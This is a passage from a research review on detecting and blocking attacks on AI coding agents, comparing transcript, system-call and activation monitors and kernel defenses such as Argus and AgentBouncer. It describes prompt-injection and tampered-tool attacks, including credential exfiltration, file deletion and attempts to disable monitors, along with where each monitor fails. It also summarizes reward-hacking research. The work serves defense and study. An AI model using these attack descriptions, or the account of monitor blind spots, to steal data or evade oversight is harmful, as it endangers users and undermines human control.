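|---|---|---|---|---|
| High-stakes user prompts | 69 | 0.957 | 37.8% | 64.2% |
| Refusals by Llama-3.2-3B | 372 | 0.935 | 61.3% | 71.9% |
| Injections in AgentDojo | 100 | 0.799 | 5.3% | 2.6% |
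| Failed tasks in ST-WebAgentBench | 23 | 0.871 | no valid threshold | no valid threshold |

ST-WebAgentBench, a set of tasks in business software, had too few harmless calibration cases for either budget, so Gao set no threshold and raised no alarms. The AgentDojo test also had fewer than the 40 harmful cases Gao had required in advance.

Activations improved detection in the first two settings. For high-stakes prompts, adding them raised the share caught by 26 percentage points (95% interval 15 to 43). For refusals, the gain was about 11 points (8 to 14), and it was still 8 points on requests that did not overlap with the training data. At a 10% budget, the gains shrank to 8 and 4 points, and the gain for high-stakes prompts was no longer distinguishable from zero. The text monitor for high-stakes prompts used only word patterns, so a stronger text monitor might reduce the gain from activations.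 Neither combined monitor reached the 80% detection rate that Gao set as the standard for a usable alarm, and neither setting involves tools.

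## A paired test of transcripts and system calls

Gao's tests combined a model's activations with its text. King and colleagues ran a similar comparison, combining an agent's text with its system calls. Their corpus, Agent Cross-Layer Evidence (ACE), has both transcripts and system calls for 4,047 agent sessions. It contains no activations, but their comparison is the closest published test of whether two records of the same agent reveal more attacks than one.

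### One container and one tracer per session

In each session, Claude Code carried out one prompt inside a fresh Docker container, an isolated environment with its own files and process numbers. It used Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model from October 2025. Inside the container, `strace` recorded 15 types of system call made by the agent and all its child processes, covering programs, files and network connections. King and colleagues also saved the agent's transcript and the list of tools that each connected MCP server advertised at the start. The median session lasted 8.8 seconds.

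This setup makes events easy to attribute to sessions. No process outside a container can descend from the traced process inside it, and each tracer writes to its own log, so events from two sessions cannot mix. To check this, King and colleagues ran three containers at once, repeated this ten times, and had the programs in each container use a tag unique to their session. The tracers recorded 8,240 events, and none carried another session's tag.

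The method does not match system calls to individual tool calls, and King and colleagues describe that matching as a harder open problem. Linking system calls to activations would require it, because activations belong to particular requests. The method also does not cover agents that run directly on a shared machine, were already running when the tracer started, or are built into code editors.

### Attacks and labels

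About half of the sessions use MCP servers. King and colleagues wrote malicious changes to the code of 31 real servers, imitating an attacker who has taken over a package. In the other sessions, the harmful instruction comes from a file, a web page, the agent's memory file, a retrieved document or the user. All the credentials are fake, and a local server intercepts outgoing traffic, so the attacks appear to succeed without sending anything to the outside world.

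Most attack designs come with a rule that checks whether the attack took effect. For a credential theft, the rule might look for a system call that opens the credentials file, followed by one that sends data to the attacker's address. The 4,047 sessions divide as follows:

| Sessions | Number | Treatment in the test |
|---|---|---|
| Attack present, and the rule found its effect | 1,358 | Malicious |
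| No attack | 1,225 | Harmless |
| Attack present, but the agent never used the tampered tool or content | 1,002 | Harmless |
| Attack of a kind that leaves no trace in either record | 66 | Harmless |
| Agent used the tampered tool or content, but the rule found no effect | 396 | Left out |

Many of these labels come from the same evidence that the detectors read. Of the 141 attack designs, 70 have a rule that checks only system calls, 57 have one that checks text at least in part, and 14 have no rule. A detector that reads system calls has an advantage when system calls also determine the label. King and colleagues therefore repeated the comparison on 239 malicious sessions in which the effect appears at least partly in the text. On unfamiliar attacks, the fine-tuned language models and the pretrained table models still did better with the host record than with the application record. The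 labels may inflate the host record's advantage, but they can't explain all of it.

Some of the 396 omitted sessions probably show exposure without commitment. For injected shell commands, the study omitted 225 sessions, almost as many as the 264 successful attacks. When King and colleagues rescored seven trained detectors with the omitted sessions counted as attacks, AUROC changed by between −0.045 and +0.010, so the detectors must have ranked many of these sessions above harmless ones. An operator who wants alarms only for real damage would consider alarms on these sessions false, but none of the study's label definitions treats them that way.

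### Features and detectors

Four of the ten detectors read each session as a list of 86 numbers. The host record supplies 57 of them:

- three totals, such as the number of system calls
- the count, the logarithm of the count and the share of the total for each of 14 types of system call
- eight comparisons between types, such as writes relative to reads
- four counts of distinct network addresses and file paths

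The application record supplies the other 29. Four describe the prompt, such as its length. Ten describe the advertised tools, including how often their descriptions use commands. Thirteen describe the tool calls and their results, and two measure how much the results contain words or markers that don't appear in earlier text.

None of the 86 features contains a file name or an address, so an attacker cannot evade detection by renaming a file, and the detectors cannot memorize names used in the corpus. Leaving out names and addresses also discards useful evidence, because the features can show that a session opened more files than usual but not that one of those files held credentials.

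AdaBoost and XGBoost build many small decision trees from these numbers. TabPFN and TabICL are neural networks pretrained on tables, and they receive the training sessions as examples when they make a prediction. The other six detectors are language models that read text instead of the 86 numbers. Three are large Qwen3 models that received descriptions of common attacks and 14 labelled examples. The other three are smaller models that King and colleagues fine-tuned on the corpus. For the host record, the language models read a short summary that lists the number of system calls of each type, the addresses contacted and the names of temporary files.

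King and colleagues tested every detector in two ways. In the first test, all 12 attack types appeared in both the training and the test data. In the second, they grouped the attack types into seven families and left one family out of training each time, along with harmless sessions from the same servers and tools. The second test is a better guide to how a detector would handle an attack its developers had not anticipated.

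### Results on familiar and unfamiliar attacks

When the attack types were familiar, all ten detectors did best with both records. XGBoost, for example, had an AUROC of 0.922 with the application record, 0.931 with the host record and 0.988 with both. Unfamiliar attacks were considerably harder:

| Detector | Application record | Host record | Both |
|---|---|---|---|
| AdaBoost | 0.689 | 0.733 | 0.840 |
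| XGBoost | 0.703 | 0.750 | 0.850 |
| TabPFN | 0.633 | 0.777 | 0.874 |
| TabICL | 0.636 | 0.764 | 0.801 |
| Qwen3-235B | 0.705 | 0.775 | 0.829 |
| Qwen3-80B | 0.678 | 0.725 | 0.810 |
| Qwen3-32B | 0.672 | 0.741 | 0.723 |
| Qwen2.5-3B, fine-tuned | 0.713 | 0.901 | 0.881 |
| Qwen2.5-7B, fine-tuned | 0.722 | 0.882 | 0.920 |
| Llama-3.1-8B, fine-tuned | 0.688 | 0.922 | 0.791 |

Seven of the ten detectors did best with both records. Adding the host record to the application record improved all ten, by 0.05 to 0.24, and every 95% interval for the gain was above zero. Adding the application record to the host record helped less reliably. Only AdaBoost, XGBoost, TabPFN and Qwen3-80B improved by more than chance could easily explain. Llama became clearly worse, and the other five results were too uncertain to show whether the detectors improved. The case for also collecting system calls is therefore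 fairly strong for a company that already logs its agents' text.

The best score in the table, 0.922, comes from Llama given only the host record, but much of it depends on addresses and temporary file names. When King and colleagues replaced nearly all of these with placeholders and retrained the model, it scored 0.759, about the same as XGBoost on the host record. Some of the lost information would be real evidence in practice, because where data goes is important, but some may be specific to the corpus. Temporary file names are the more likely shortcut, because only 2.7% of malicious sessions contacted the reserved address ranges used in the fake thefts. The 0.922 is therefore not a reliable estimate of how well system calls alone would work against a new attacker.

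Llama's drop to 0.791 with both records shows that more evidence can make a detector worse. King and colleagues attribute the drop to overfitting, meaning that the model learned details of the training transcripts that did not carry over to other attacks. A joined record is also of little use to a monitor that doesn't know what ordinary agent activity looks like. When the Qwen3 models received neither examples nor descriptions of attacks, they scored 0.57 to 0.59 on the application record and 0.50 to 0.52, close to chance, on both records.

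The order of the system calls mattered very little. Four neural networks that read the raw stream of events scored between 0.517 and 0.578 on unfamiliar attacks, while a small language model trained on the summary scored 0.836. The lowest score came from a network that learned normal sequences from harmless sessions, which is close to the method Forrest and colleagues introduced in 1996. This fits the earlier concern that agents have no stable sequences to learn, although the short sessions may also have disadvantaged these networks.

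### Where each record helps

The results by attack type explain why the two records work well together. The next table gives the average AUROC of the ten detectors on familiar attacks, for half of the 12 types:

| Attack type | Malicious sessions | Application record | Host record | Both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Silent exfiltration through logs | 244 | 0.586 | 0.976 | 0.970 |
| Audit-log poisoning | 11 | 0.608 | 0.932 | 0.954 |
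| Direct reading of credentials | 227 | 0.876 | 0.882 | 0.978 |
| Injection in tool metadata | 113 | 0.783 | 0.756 | 0.902 |
| Retrieval reference injection | 53 | 0.906 | 0.703 | 0.927 |
| Preference manipulation | 29 | 0.687 | 0.701 | 0.834 |

In silent exfiltration through logs, a tampered tool reads credentials and writes them to a log while doing its normal job. Neither step appears in the transcript, so the host record is nearly sufficient without the application record, which is almost useless here. This is the "host alarm only" case from the earlier table of alarm combinations.

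Conversely, retrieval reference injection, the text-only attack mentioned earlier, leaves no distinctive system calls, yet detectors using the host record still reach an AUROC of 0.703 on it. They may be picking up incidental differences between the malicious and harmless sessions, such as different tasks or files. If so, similar differences could be raising the other scores on familiar attacks.

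Preference manipulation, in which planted content steers the agent's choices, was the only type of attack for which neither record alone reached 0.75, the study's threshold for acceptable performance. Together they reached 0.834. There were only 29 malicious sessions, so this is suggestive evidence that combining two weak signals can produce a useful one.

The study gave one detector the features or text from both records, whereas the AND and OR rules described earlier combine the alarms of two separate detectors. A single detector can learn that starting fifty programs is normal when the prompt is for a build and unusual when it is for a summary. Neither rule can do this, so an operator who combines alarms from two separate products might not see the gains reported in ACE. King and colleagues also do not report how often false alarms from the two records coincide, but the corpus could provide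 that figure once they release it.

### Off-the-shelf tools

Falco is a widely used open-source program that checks Linux system calls against a set of rules. King and colleagues applied its default rules to ACE, except those that need information the tracer did not collect. Falco normally raises an alarm when any rule matches. At least one rule matched in every session, so it detected 100% of the attacks with a false-positive rate of 100%. Ranking sessions by the number of different rules that matched gave an AUROC of 0.572 on unfamiliar attacks.

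The rules separated harmless sessions from malicious ones poorly because they are designed for a long-running server, where starting a shell, reading a sensitive file or creating a hidden temporary file is suspicious. Claude Code does all three in ordinary work. The rule for sensitive files matched in every harmless session, partly because programs routinely open `/etc/passwd` as they start. A rule for connections to unusual network ports was more informative but still missed most attacks, matching 4.6% of harmless sessions and 13.4% of malicious ones.

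Commercial products have a similar problem. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* describes coding agents on customers' Windows machines triggering rules the company wrote to catch human intruders.

Rules written for agents may do much better. In *AgentSpy*, Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2026) recorded the system calls of agents inside small virtual machines and checked them against prohibitions, such as reading private keys. Their general rules detected four of five categories of attack through malicious Skills and raised no false alarms in 50 runs. But Gao requires 59 clean runs to establish even a 5% false-positive rate, so 50 are too few to establish a rate low enough for everyday use.

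Scanning tools before installation did not solve the problem either. Cisco's scanner for MCP servers, which reads the advertised list of tools, flagged 15.9% of the malicious sessions that used these servers and 16.3% of the others. Of the 82 malicious server designs, 52 change what the server does but not its advertised tools, so a scanner that reads only the list cannot detect them.

On the same sessions, the trained detectors did far better, at least against familiar attacks. At a false-positive rate below 1%, XGBoost, using both records, caught 86% of the attacks, and Llama, using only the host record, caught 82%. Qwen3-80B caught less than 1% because it gave many malicious and harmless sessions the same high score, so no threshold could separate them.

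Even with XGBoost, most alarms would be false if attacks were rare. Its actual false-positive rate at this setting was 0.88%. Over 10,000 sessions with ten attacks, it would catch about nine attacks and raise 88 false alarms. King and colleagues chose the thresholds using the test sessions, so XGBoost would probably do somewhat worse in a real deployment. Unfamiliar attacks would lower the detection rate further.

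### A different agent

All of ACE comes from one model and one agent program. To find out whether the detectors would work elsewhere, King and colleagues recorded another 592 sessions, called ACE-XA, with Mistral's Devstral 2 model and a simple agent program of their own. They trained each detector on ACE sessions from one attack family and tested it on ACE-XA sessions from the same family, covering five families in all. (Qwen3-80B received two labelled examples instead of training.)

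| Detector | Records | Average AUROC | AUROC on credential theft |
|---|---|---|---|
| XGBoost | Both | 0.842 | 0.718 |
| TabPFN | Both | 0.662 | 0.418 |
| Qwen3-80B | Both | 0.998 | 0.993 |
| Llama-3.1-8B, fine-tuned | Host | 0.849 | 0.605 |

King and colleagues traced TabPFN's poor result mainly to one feature, the number of distinct paths under `/tmp`, the folder for temporary files. Claude Code always writes some files there, so the number is never zero in ACE. The new agent program keeps tool results in memory, and the number is zero in 57% of its sessions. TabPFN had no earlier examples with a zero, so the zeros led to wrong predictions, whereas XGBoost could make its predictions mostly without the feature.

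An update to an agent program could cause the same failure. If Claude Code moved its temporary files, a detector trained on the old version might misclassify every session, even though neither the users nor the attackers had changed. Operators who train detectors on system calls should retest them after each update to the agent program.

Qwen3-80B's near-perfect score probably reflects the design of the test more than the model's ability. The malicious sessions in ACE-XA come from only 13 attack designs and the purely harmless ones from seven templates, so the two groups may be easy to distinguish. The test also uses familiar attack families, and the study did not test the harder case of an unfamiliar kind of attack on an unfamiliar agent.

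### How far the results extend

Real sessions differ in length as well as variety from those in ACE, which usually last a few seconds. The features describe a whole session, so in an hour-long session with hundreds of tool calls, one extra file read and one extra connection would barely change the totals. A probe that averages over too many tokens has the same problem. Scoring shorter stretches of activity might help, but that requires matching system calls to tool calls, a problem the study doesn't solve.

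The detectors also scored each session only after it had ended, so ACE can't show how early they would have raised an alarm. By the time a session ends, a stolen credential may already be in use. To block an attack, a detector would have to score the session after each system call or tool call, with much less evidence.

The simulated network probably makes the attacks look more uniform than real ones. The local server accepts every connection, so each attempted theft produces the system calls of a successful upload. In real attacks, some uploads would fail, and the agent or the malicious program might then try something else. Attackers who knew about the detector could also slow down or imitate ordinary work to avoid it, but no attacker in the study tried to evade detection.

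The application record also has gaps. Only 2,871 of the 4,047 sessions include the user's initial prompt, which is often what distinguishes an authorized action from a theft. When King and colleagues limited the test to those sessions, all six language models still did better with either the host record or both records than with the application record alone. Scores on the application record rose by less than 0.05 for the three fine-tuned models and fell for the three large Qwen3 models. Missing prompts therefore don't appear to explain why the application record did worse.

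### Whether direct evidence exists

As of December 2026, searches of research papers and the web have found no study that combines activations and system calls from the same agent. Several studies come close, using either activations or system calls.

AgentSight and AgentLoupe link system calls to the text of the model's responses. *Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* (2026) presents Argus, which connects events inside the agent's software to the operating-system actions that follow. None of the three uses the model's activations.

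Chauhan and Revankar combined their activation probe with decoy credentials planted in the model's context. If a decoy appears in the model's output, something has made the model leak it. Like a join with the host record, this design has two independent sources of evidence, but both concern the model's input and output, so it would miss a decoy that left the machine through a tool's own code.

Wilhelm and Kao (2026), in *From Reward-Hack Activations to Agentic Risk States*, come closest to linking a model's internal states to host system activity. They studied reward hacking, in which a model satisfies the measure of success without doing the intended task. Their agents played a text-based household game that offered ways to cheat, such as choosing an easy grader or claiming that a task was complete. Some of the models had training that encouraged reward hacking. At each step, a classifier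 scored the model's activations for signs of reward hacking, and a second model combined this score with other information to predict whether the next action would be bad.

For a Qwen model, the activation score alone predicted bad actions with an AUROC of 0.565, barely better than chance. Adding the model's uncertainty about its next token and facts about the situation, such as the previous action and whether a way to cheat was available, raised the AUROC to 0.667. For the narrower category of explicit cheating, which had only 184 positive cases, the activation score alone reached 0.769, and the full combination did not improve on this, scoring 0.756.

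A version of the model trained on an even mix of harmless and reward-hacking examples cheated more often than the version with the highest average activation score. Wilhelm and Kao conclude that the score describes a tendency, which leads to a bad action only when the situation allows it. For a real agent, a host record could supply some of that context, such as whether a credentials file is readable or outgoing connections work. This is an inference from a game in which the researchers defined every possible action in advance.

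### What activations would change

ACE can't be used to test this directly, because King and colleagues ran Claude through Amazon's cloud service, which returns text but not activations. The results by attack type still suggest where activations might help.

Activations should add almost nothing to the detection of silent exfiltration through logs, because the model's context contains no sign of the theft. A monitor that used activations instead of the transcript would need the host record just as much to detect this attack.

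Injections in retrieved text or tool metadata are more promising, since probes detect exposure well. The text detectors in ACE already do fairly well on familiar attacks of this kind, so probes would need to do better on unfamiliar ones. They may not, because Iris, the probe by Alfano and colleagues, lost its lead over text monitors on unfamiliar material. The largest gain might come from the 396 sessions that ACE leaves out. A probe trained to predict commitment could help distinguish an agent that obeyed an injection from one that ignored it, although Sinha found that a simple text classifier did this about as well.

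Replacing the transcript with activations would also remove the command that the model wrote, which an operator uses to link a request to a process and to explain an alarm to an analyst. Probe scores don't include that command, so activations make more sense as a third record alongside the transcript and system calls.

A first experiment that takes little compute would be to run ACE's transcripts through a small open-weight model and probe that model's activations. Dong and colleagues' results suggest this should detect exposure, but it would not reveal Claude's own state. With ACE-XA, researchers could instead recompute the activations of the model that acted, because Mistral has published Devstral 2's weights. They would first have to restore the users' prompts, which are missing from all 592 records, and the rest of the context the model received.

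A new corpus would give a cleaner answer. Researchers could run an open-weight agent in containers as King and colleagues did, save its activations, and compare detectors that use text and system calls with detectors that also use activations. The difference in performance on unfamiliar attacks would measure what activations add. The labels should draw on each attack's intended effect, the agent's tool calls, and the system calls, so that no record has a built-in advantage. Recording thousands of sessions need not be expensive. The model fees for all 4,047 ACE sessions came to about $164, though an open-weight model would need its own GPUs.

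## Systems that trace or block agents in the kernel

The detectors King and colleagues tested on ACE scored sessions that had already ended. A system that runs beside a live agent has to identify which processes belong to the agent and follow data from one process to another. To prevent a theft, it also has to check a system call before the kernel executes it. Several groups built such systems in 2026, none of which reads the model's activations. Their results therefore show how much a monitor can do with host events and the user's request, without a probe.

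### Telling an agent from ordinary tools

Agents start shells, edit files and contact servers, but so does much of the other software on a developer's machine. Canale and Soulis (2026), in *Detecting Shadow AI*, ran into this problem on Windows, where they wanted to find agents that employees use without their company's approval. They call two programs behavioural twins if they have the same process trees, connections and timing but contact different services. Let β(p) be everything observable about a program p except the names and addresses that identify software or services. For any detector f that reads only β,

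if β(a) = β(b), then f(β(a)) = f(β(b))

Given an agent and a script that queries a package index, the detector either misses the agent or flags the script.

Canale and Soulis tested two detection rules on 12 synthetic agents and nine harmless workloads, three of which were twins of the agents. The first rule flagged any interpreter, such as Python, with an encrypted connection and a shell among its descendant processes. It caught nine agents. A looser rule that applied the same test to any program caught ten. Each rule also flagged four harmless workloads: the three twins and `npm install`, a common command that downloads JavaScript packages and runs their setup scripts.

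Their own detector also identifies the service a process is contacting, using either Windows' cache of recent DNS lookups or the address ranges that some AI providers publish. It then checks whether the process runs commands. It caught all 12 agents in most of five runs and flagged none of the harmless workloads.

These are best-case figures because Canale and Soulis had corrected the detector after seeing its mistakes on some of the same workloads, and they scanned each agent within seconds of its start. When a provider shared its addresses with other websites, the detector could identify an open connection for at most five minutes. It detected an agent that connected only intermittently in 15 of 40 scans run at random times.

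Identity evidence shows that a process is communicating with a model, but a monitor also needs the user's request to judge whether the process is doing harm, as the earlier example of the two credential uploads showed.

### Following data through files

On Linux, an operator can avoid much of the identification problem by attaching a monitor to a known agent process and following its descendants. This fails when data passes through a file to an unrelated program, as in the crontab attack that Bao and colleagues traced. Cui and colleagues designed Agent-Warden for such cases. Like AgentLoupe, it passes labels from a process to its children, to the files it writes and to any process that reads those files.

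A fourth rule labels a parent process when its labelled child exits. This keeps very short-lived helper programs connected to the agent's activity, but it also labels parents that never used the child's output. Renaming a file does not remove its label, because the label is attached to the kernel's record of the file, not its name.

In the main test, an agent's script wrote a temporary file and renamed it. A monitoring script, which the agent had not started, later read the file. Both versions of Agent-Warden reconstructed the whole chain in all 30 runs on each of two types of processor. Langfuse, which logs what the agent software reports, could not follow the chain past the file. Cui and colleagues wrote the test to exercise their four rules, so it confirms that the rules work as designed but not that they stay precise on a busy machine.

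Agent-Warden tracks only processes and files, so in the running example it would show `curl` reading the credentials file but not the upload. Its labels disappear when the machine restarts, so it could not trace a job scheduled for the following month if the machine restarted first. It also only observes activity, so it could not have stopped the theft.

### How Argus turns a request into permissions

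*Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* presents Argus, a system that checks whether an agent's operations fit the user's request and can stop those that don't.

Argus must first identify the user's request. It hooks the function that encrypts the agent's messages to the model so that it can copy each message before encryption. Agent software sometimes puts tool output in the same field as the user's words, so Argus accepts text as the user's only if kernel monitoring also shows it arriving through the command line, the terminal or a user interface that the operator has registered. This check excludes a hidden comment in a README, for example, because it arrives through none of these.

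A language model then lists the files and hosts named in the request and what the user wants done with each. Argus discards any entry that the request's wording does not support. For example, "Summarize report.txt" gives the agent permission to read the file but not to change or delete it. The agent may also read and change files in its working folder, and the operator can allow common actions such as connecting to a package registry.

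Argus lets most operations go ahead without a decision. It only logs file reads, but it checks operations that could affect something outside the task, such as sending data over the network, changing files outside the working folder or deleting files that existed before the session. If the kernel finds no matching permission, it pauses the process before the operation takes effect and restarts the system call only if Argus approves it.

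Argus also tracks data from sensitive files, such as SSH keys and cloud credentials. A process that opens such a file becomes tainted, and the taint spreads to its child processes, to files it writes, and through pipes to other processes. Argus applies further checks to a tainted process's connections unless the user named the destination. This stops an attacker from uploading a stolen key to a popular site that the operator allows for everyone.

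Tool output returns to the agent through a pipe, so reading one key taints the agent and every command it starts afterwards. The taint therefore still applies when the model copies a secret into a later command. However, even a routine connection to the package registry then needs closer inspection for the rest of the session.

### Rules for clear cases, a model for unclear ones

For a paused file operation, Argus compares the path with the files named in the request, first as written and then after resolving symbolic links. A match with the right permission is enough to allow the operation. For a connection, Argus checks whether the address belongs to a host that the user or operator has allowed.

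Argus sends the remaining cases to a second language model, the auditor, which was GPT-4.1-mini in the tests. The auditor receives the user's request, the operation, the chain of processes that led to it and the session's earlier accesses to sensitive files. It can approve the operation only with a confidence of at least 0.7. Argus withholds the agent's conversation from the auditor because an agent that has read an injection may repeat the attacker's address in its own words, which would make the address look like part of the task.

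If the auditor rejects the operation or does not answer in time, Argus kills the process that attempted it, along with its descendants. The agent keeps running, sees that the command failed and can try another way to finish the task. After ten interventions, Argus ends the session.

In the running example, the user asked only for a build. `curl` can read the credentials file, but its connection to 203.0.113.9 matches no permission, so Argus pauses it and consults the auditor. The `setup.sh` variant leads to the same check, because Argus evaluates the connection rather than the command that led to it. The auditor's decision then determines whether the theft fails.

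### Results on ORBIT

The Argus paper also introduces ORBIT, a benchmark that runs an agent's commands in a real shell instead of simulating them. It has 126 attack runs and 43 harmless ones. Eight groups of attacks each combine five user tasks with three malicious instructions, and a ninth contains six attacks that probe Argus's permission rules. Each successful attack leaves a particular trace, such as a marker file, and the benchmark checks for that trace independently of Argus's alarms. Each scenario ran five times, and an attack counted as successful if it worked at least once.

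| Model | Attack success without Argus | Attack success with Argus | Harmless runs with an alarm | User tasks completed with Argus |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 | 97.3% | 38.9% | 0% | 98.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 55.9% | 27.9% | 4.7% | 98.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 8.1% | 0% | 0% | 96.8% |
| GLM-5.2 | 56.8% | 36.9% | 27.9% | 97.6% |

The defense success rate (the share of attacks that failed) therefore ranged from 61.1% to 100%. Agents completed 96.8% to 98.4% of the users' tasks. Both ranges somewhat overstate how well Argus performs.

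The defense success rate includes attacks that the model refused by itself. Opus 4.7 refused most attacks, and Sonnet 4.6 refused every attack in three of the nine groups. The averages also cover different attacks, because GPT-5.1's includes a group of 15 attacks that try to disable Argus and the other three models' averages do not. Without that group, the per-group results give GPT-5.1 a defense success rate of 55.9%.

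The task completion figures match the attack runs, although the paper's conclusion attributes them to harmless ones. An agent that did both the user's task and the attacker's would still count as having completed its task. Alarms in harmless runs are a better guide to how much Argus would burden ordinary users, and they varied widely. With GLM-5.2, Argus raised alarms in 12 of the 43 harmless runs, including all five that involved web content.

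Argus did best against conspicuous attacks. For GPT-5.1, it cut the success rate of injected shell commands from 100% to zero. Instructions hidden in web pages, local files and search results were much harder to stop, and 53% to 80% of these attacks still succeeded on the three models other than Opus. They rely on file reads and web requests that also occur in ordinary work, so stopping them depends more on the auditor.

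With GPT-5.1, 93.3% of attacks also succeeded when the malicious instruction was in the user's own task. This follows from the design, because Argus treats the user's words as authority and its threat model excludes such attacks. The results for the six attacks on the permission rules are more worrying. Argus stopped all six for Opus, but three still succeeded on each of the other models, at least as many as without Argus. Six attacks are too few for a reliable estimate, but they are the benchmark's closest approximation to an attacker who has studied the defense.

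None of the attempts to disable Argus worked. It runs outside the agent's process tree, and the kernel rejects the agent's attempts to send it a kill signal.

For comparison, the developers ran GPT-5.1 with CaMeL, a defense that controls the agent's plan and checks its tool calls. CaMeL stopped 69 of the 126 attacks (54.8%), eight fewer than Argus, but completed only 77.0% of the tasks. Argus therefore has a clearer advantage in usefulness than in security.

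Argus's overhead is mostly unknown. Attaching it to an agent took 21.2 milliseconds on average, but its developers did not report how long paused operations waited for the auditor, and that wait is probably the larger delay.

### Asking a model about each unusual call

Joos and Pradel (2026) did measure the full delay for a similar system, AgentBouncer. It pauses the system calls that a coding agent's tools make, decides common ones using preset rules or earlier decisions, and sends the rest to a language model. The model rates how safe each call is and how necessary it is for the task. The less necessary the call, the more certain the model must be that it is safe.

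Joos and Pradel combined 85 harmful goals with four ways of delivering an attack: an injected prompt, a malicious tool, a planted script and a repository whose tests contain the attack. AgentBouncer reduced the success rate of these 340 attacks from 99.4% to 10.6%. Without attacks, the agent solved about as many tasks with AgentBouncer as without it, and only 0.25% of harmless tool calls failed. AgentBouncer added 47 seconds and $0.0036 to each task. These are small overheads for an agent that works unattended, but a person waiting for an answer would notice the delay.

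One of the malicious tools, `validate_patch`, checks a software patch as advertised and then silently deletes `/etc/gshadow`, where Linux keeps group passwords. Two monitors that read only the agent's prompts and tool calls did not block it. AgentSentinel, which watches events on the machine, detected the deletion and killed the process, but the file was already gone. AgentBouncer blocked only the system call to delete the file, and the agent went on to solve its task.

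The attack success rates of Argus and AgentBouncer aren't comparable because the attacks and agents differ. AgentBouncer's model reads the agent's stated reason for each tool call, which provides context that Argus's auditor lacks. But an injection can influence that reason, and Argus avoids this risk by withholding the conversation from its auditor.

### Rules that the agent writes

*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026), from a team that includes developers of AgentSight, lets the agent write kernel rules for itself. The team first studied the instruction files that 64 popular software projects provide for AI agents. The kernel could in principle enforce 607 of the 1,361 instructions in these files, or 45%. The others concern matters such as the contents of files or how the agent explains itself.

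Instructions about visible actions are often too vague to enforce directly. Zheng and colleagues found that 73.6% of instructions with some observable effect on the system need information from the project or the current task. For instance, "Run the full test suite before committing" does not specify which command runs the tests. An agent that has read the project usually knows the command and can write a rule that stops `git commit` unless `go test` has finished successfully since the last change to the source code. The kernel enforces the rule even if the commit happens inside a script.

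ActPlane and Argus differ mainly in who can set the rules. Argus takes permissions from the user and the operator, while ActPlane also lets the agent write rules as it works. Argus's developers object that injected content can shape those rules. Zheng and colleagues largely accept this objection, and promise security in ActPlane only for rules loaded before the agent starts, which the agent can add to but not weaken. The agent's own rules are meant to help a cooperative agent avoid mistakes.

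In a test of 190 recorded situations, ActPlane led to the right outcome in 75.8%, compared with 45% to 49% for three systems that check tool calls. Much of the gain came from explaining each refusal to the agent. The agent corrected its behaviour after 97.7% of detected violations when it received an explanation, compared with 31.4% when it received only an error message. ActPlane also intervened wrongly in 18 of 76 situations where the agent had followed the rules, almost always because a rule was too broad.

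A second test used 361 workplace tasks that lead an agent towards unsafe actions, such as leaking credentials. GPT-5.5 wrote the rules for each task from its description before the agent started. Without ActPlane, the agent did something unsafe in 106 tasks, and ActPlane prevented this in 78 of them. Its rules also fired in 16% of the tasks that the agent had handled safely without them. With up to 100 rules loaded, ActPlane slowed the workloads by 1.9% to 8.4%.

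### Blocking without detecting

If the kernel can block a forbidden action, an operator may not need to know the model's state. *ContractWarden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) describes a simple version of this approach. For each asset, a person chooses `allow`, `deny` or `no_egress`, which keeps data from leaving the machine. A model may suggest the settings, but the person makes the final choice and the kernel enforces it.

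If the credentials file in the running example is marked `no_egress`, the upload fails whether an attacker has hijacked the model, the model has misunderstood its task, or a tampered tool has acted alone. A probe would miss the last of these cases.

A rule like this also largely avoids the base-rate problem, because a ban on something that no legitimate task requires should cause hardly any false alarms. Attackers can't evade it by rewording an injection. Writing the rules can be cheap, as GPT-5.5 translated the 607 instructions in the ActPlane study for about $0.028 each.

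For secrets that no task needs to send anywhere, the argument is convincing. An operator should block those uploads before investing in probes.

### What a policy cannot specify in advance

A rule protects only what someone has declared. ContractWarden's guarantees, for example, cover declared assets and the types of access it supports. The 28 unsafe tasks that ActPlane failed to prevent show what kernel rules miss. In some, the harm was in a chat message or in text the agent wrote to a file. In others, the agent changed data inside a separate service that ActPlane did not monitor.

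Permitted actions can do harm too. A user who asks an agent to edit a source file has to let it write to that file, and an injected instruction could make it add a security hole. The requested edit and the malicious one would both appear in the kernel as a permitted write. Argus explicitly excludes such attacks from its guarantees.

Open-ended tasks are also difficult because a user who asks an agent to research a software problem cannot list every site it will need. Restricting the agent to named sites makes the task impossible, but allowing all sites lets a theft through. Argus leaves such cases to its auditor, and its results on them were weaker. GLM-5.2's false alarms were concentrated in tasks where the agent discovers destinations as it works, and attacks through web pages and search results were among those that Argus missed most often.

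*Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira and colleagues, 2026) instead learns what is normal from earlier sessions. It records whether each argument of a tool call came from the user, a trusted source or untrusted content, and compares the pattern with past harmless runs. It settles unclear cases with a list of known values and then a language model. On two public benchmarks, it blocked 94.3% of successful injections and allowed about 95% of harmless runs. It suits agents with a narrow job, such as handling email, better than agents that write new programs every day. It also relies on the agent to report where each argument came from and assumes that the tools' code is trustworthy.

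### Whether a probe score could help

Argus's auditor often has to judge an unfamiliar destination without seeing what the agent has read. A probe score from the request that produced the tool call could supply some of that context. If the score suggested that the model was following planted instructions, the auditor would have a reason to refuse. Unlike a passage from a poisoned web page, a score cannot carry instructions to the auditor, though an attacker might still find wording that keeps the score low. No published system appears to have tested this use of a probe.

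The closest existing work blocks text instead of system calls. In *Language Model Security Modules*, Zhang, Ruan and colleagues (2026) built a layer for model servers that holds back a response until the required checks on the model's activations have finished. If a check fails to run, the server refuses the request. With probes on the open model Qwen3-4B, the success rate of harmful requests fell from 39.4% to 3.3%, while refusals of harmless requests rose from 0.8% to 3.1%. The server kept at least 96% of its normal speed.

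They also found that when a server did not keep each request's scores separate, it released 878 responses to harmful requests that the same policy would otherwise have refused. A system that used probe scores to approve system calls would face the same danger, and it would also have to match each request to a process.

Zhang and colleagues tested only single requests and left tool outputs to future work. In principle, the same layer could hold back a tool call until the probe has scored it. This would stop some attacks before they reach the host, but it would not help with a script whose contents the model never saw.

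A tampered tool can open a connection while the model behaves normally, so a low score is not by itself evidence that the connection is safe. An auditor should count a low score in favour of an operation only if the model's own tool call names the destination, and even then only as weak evidence.

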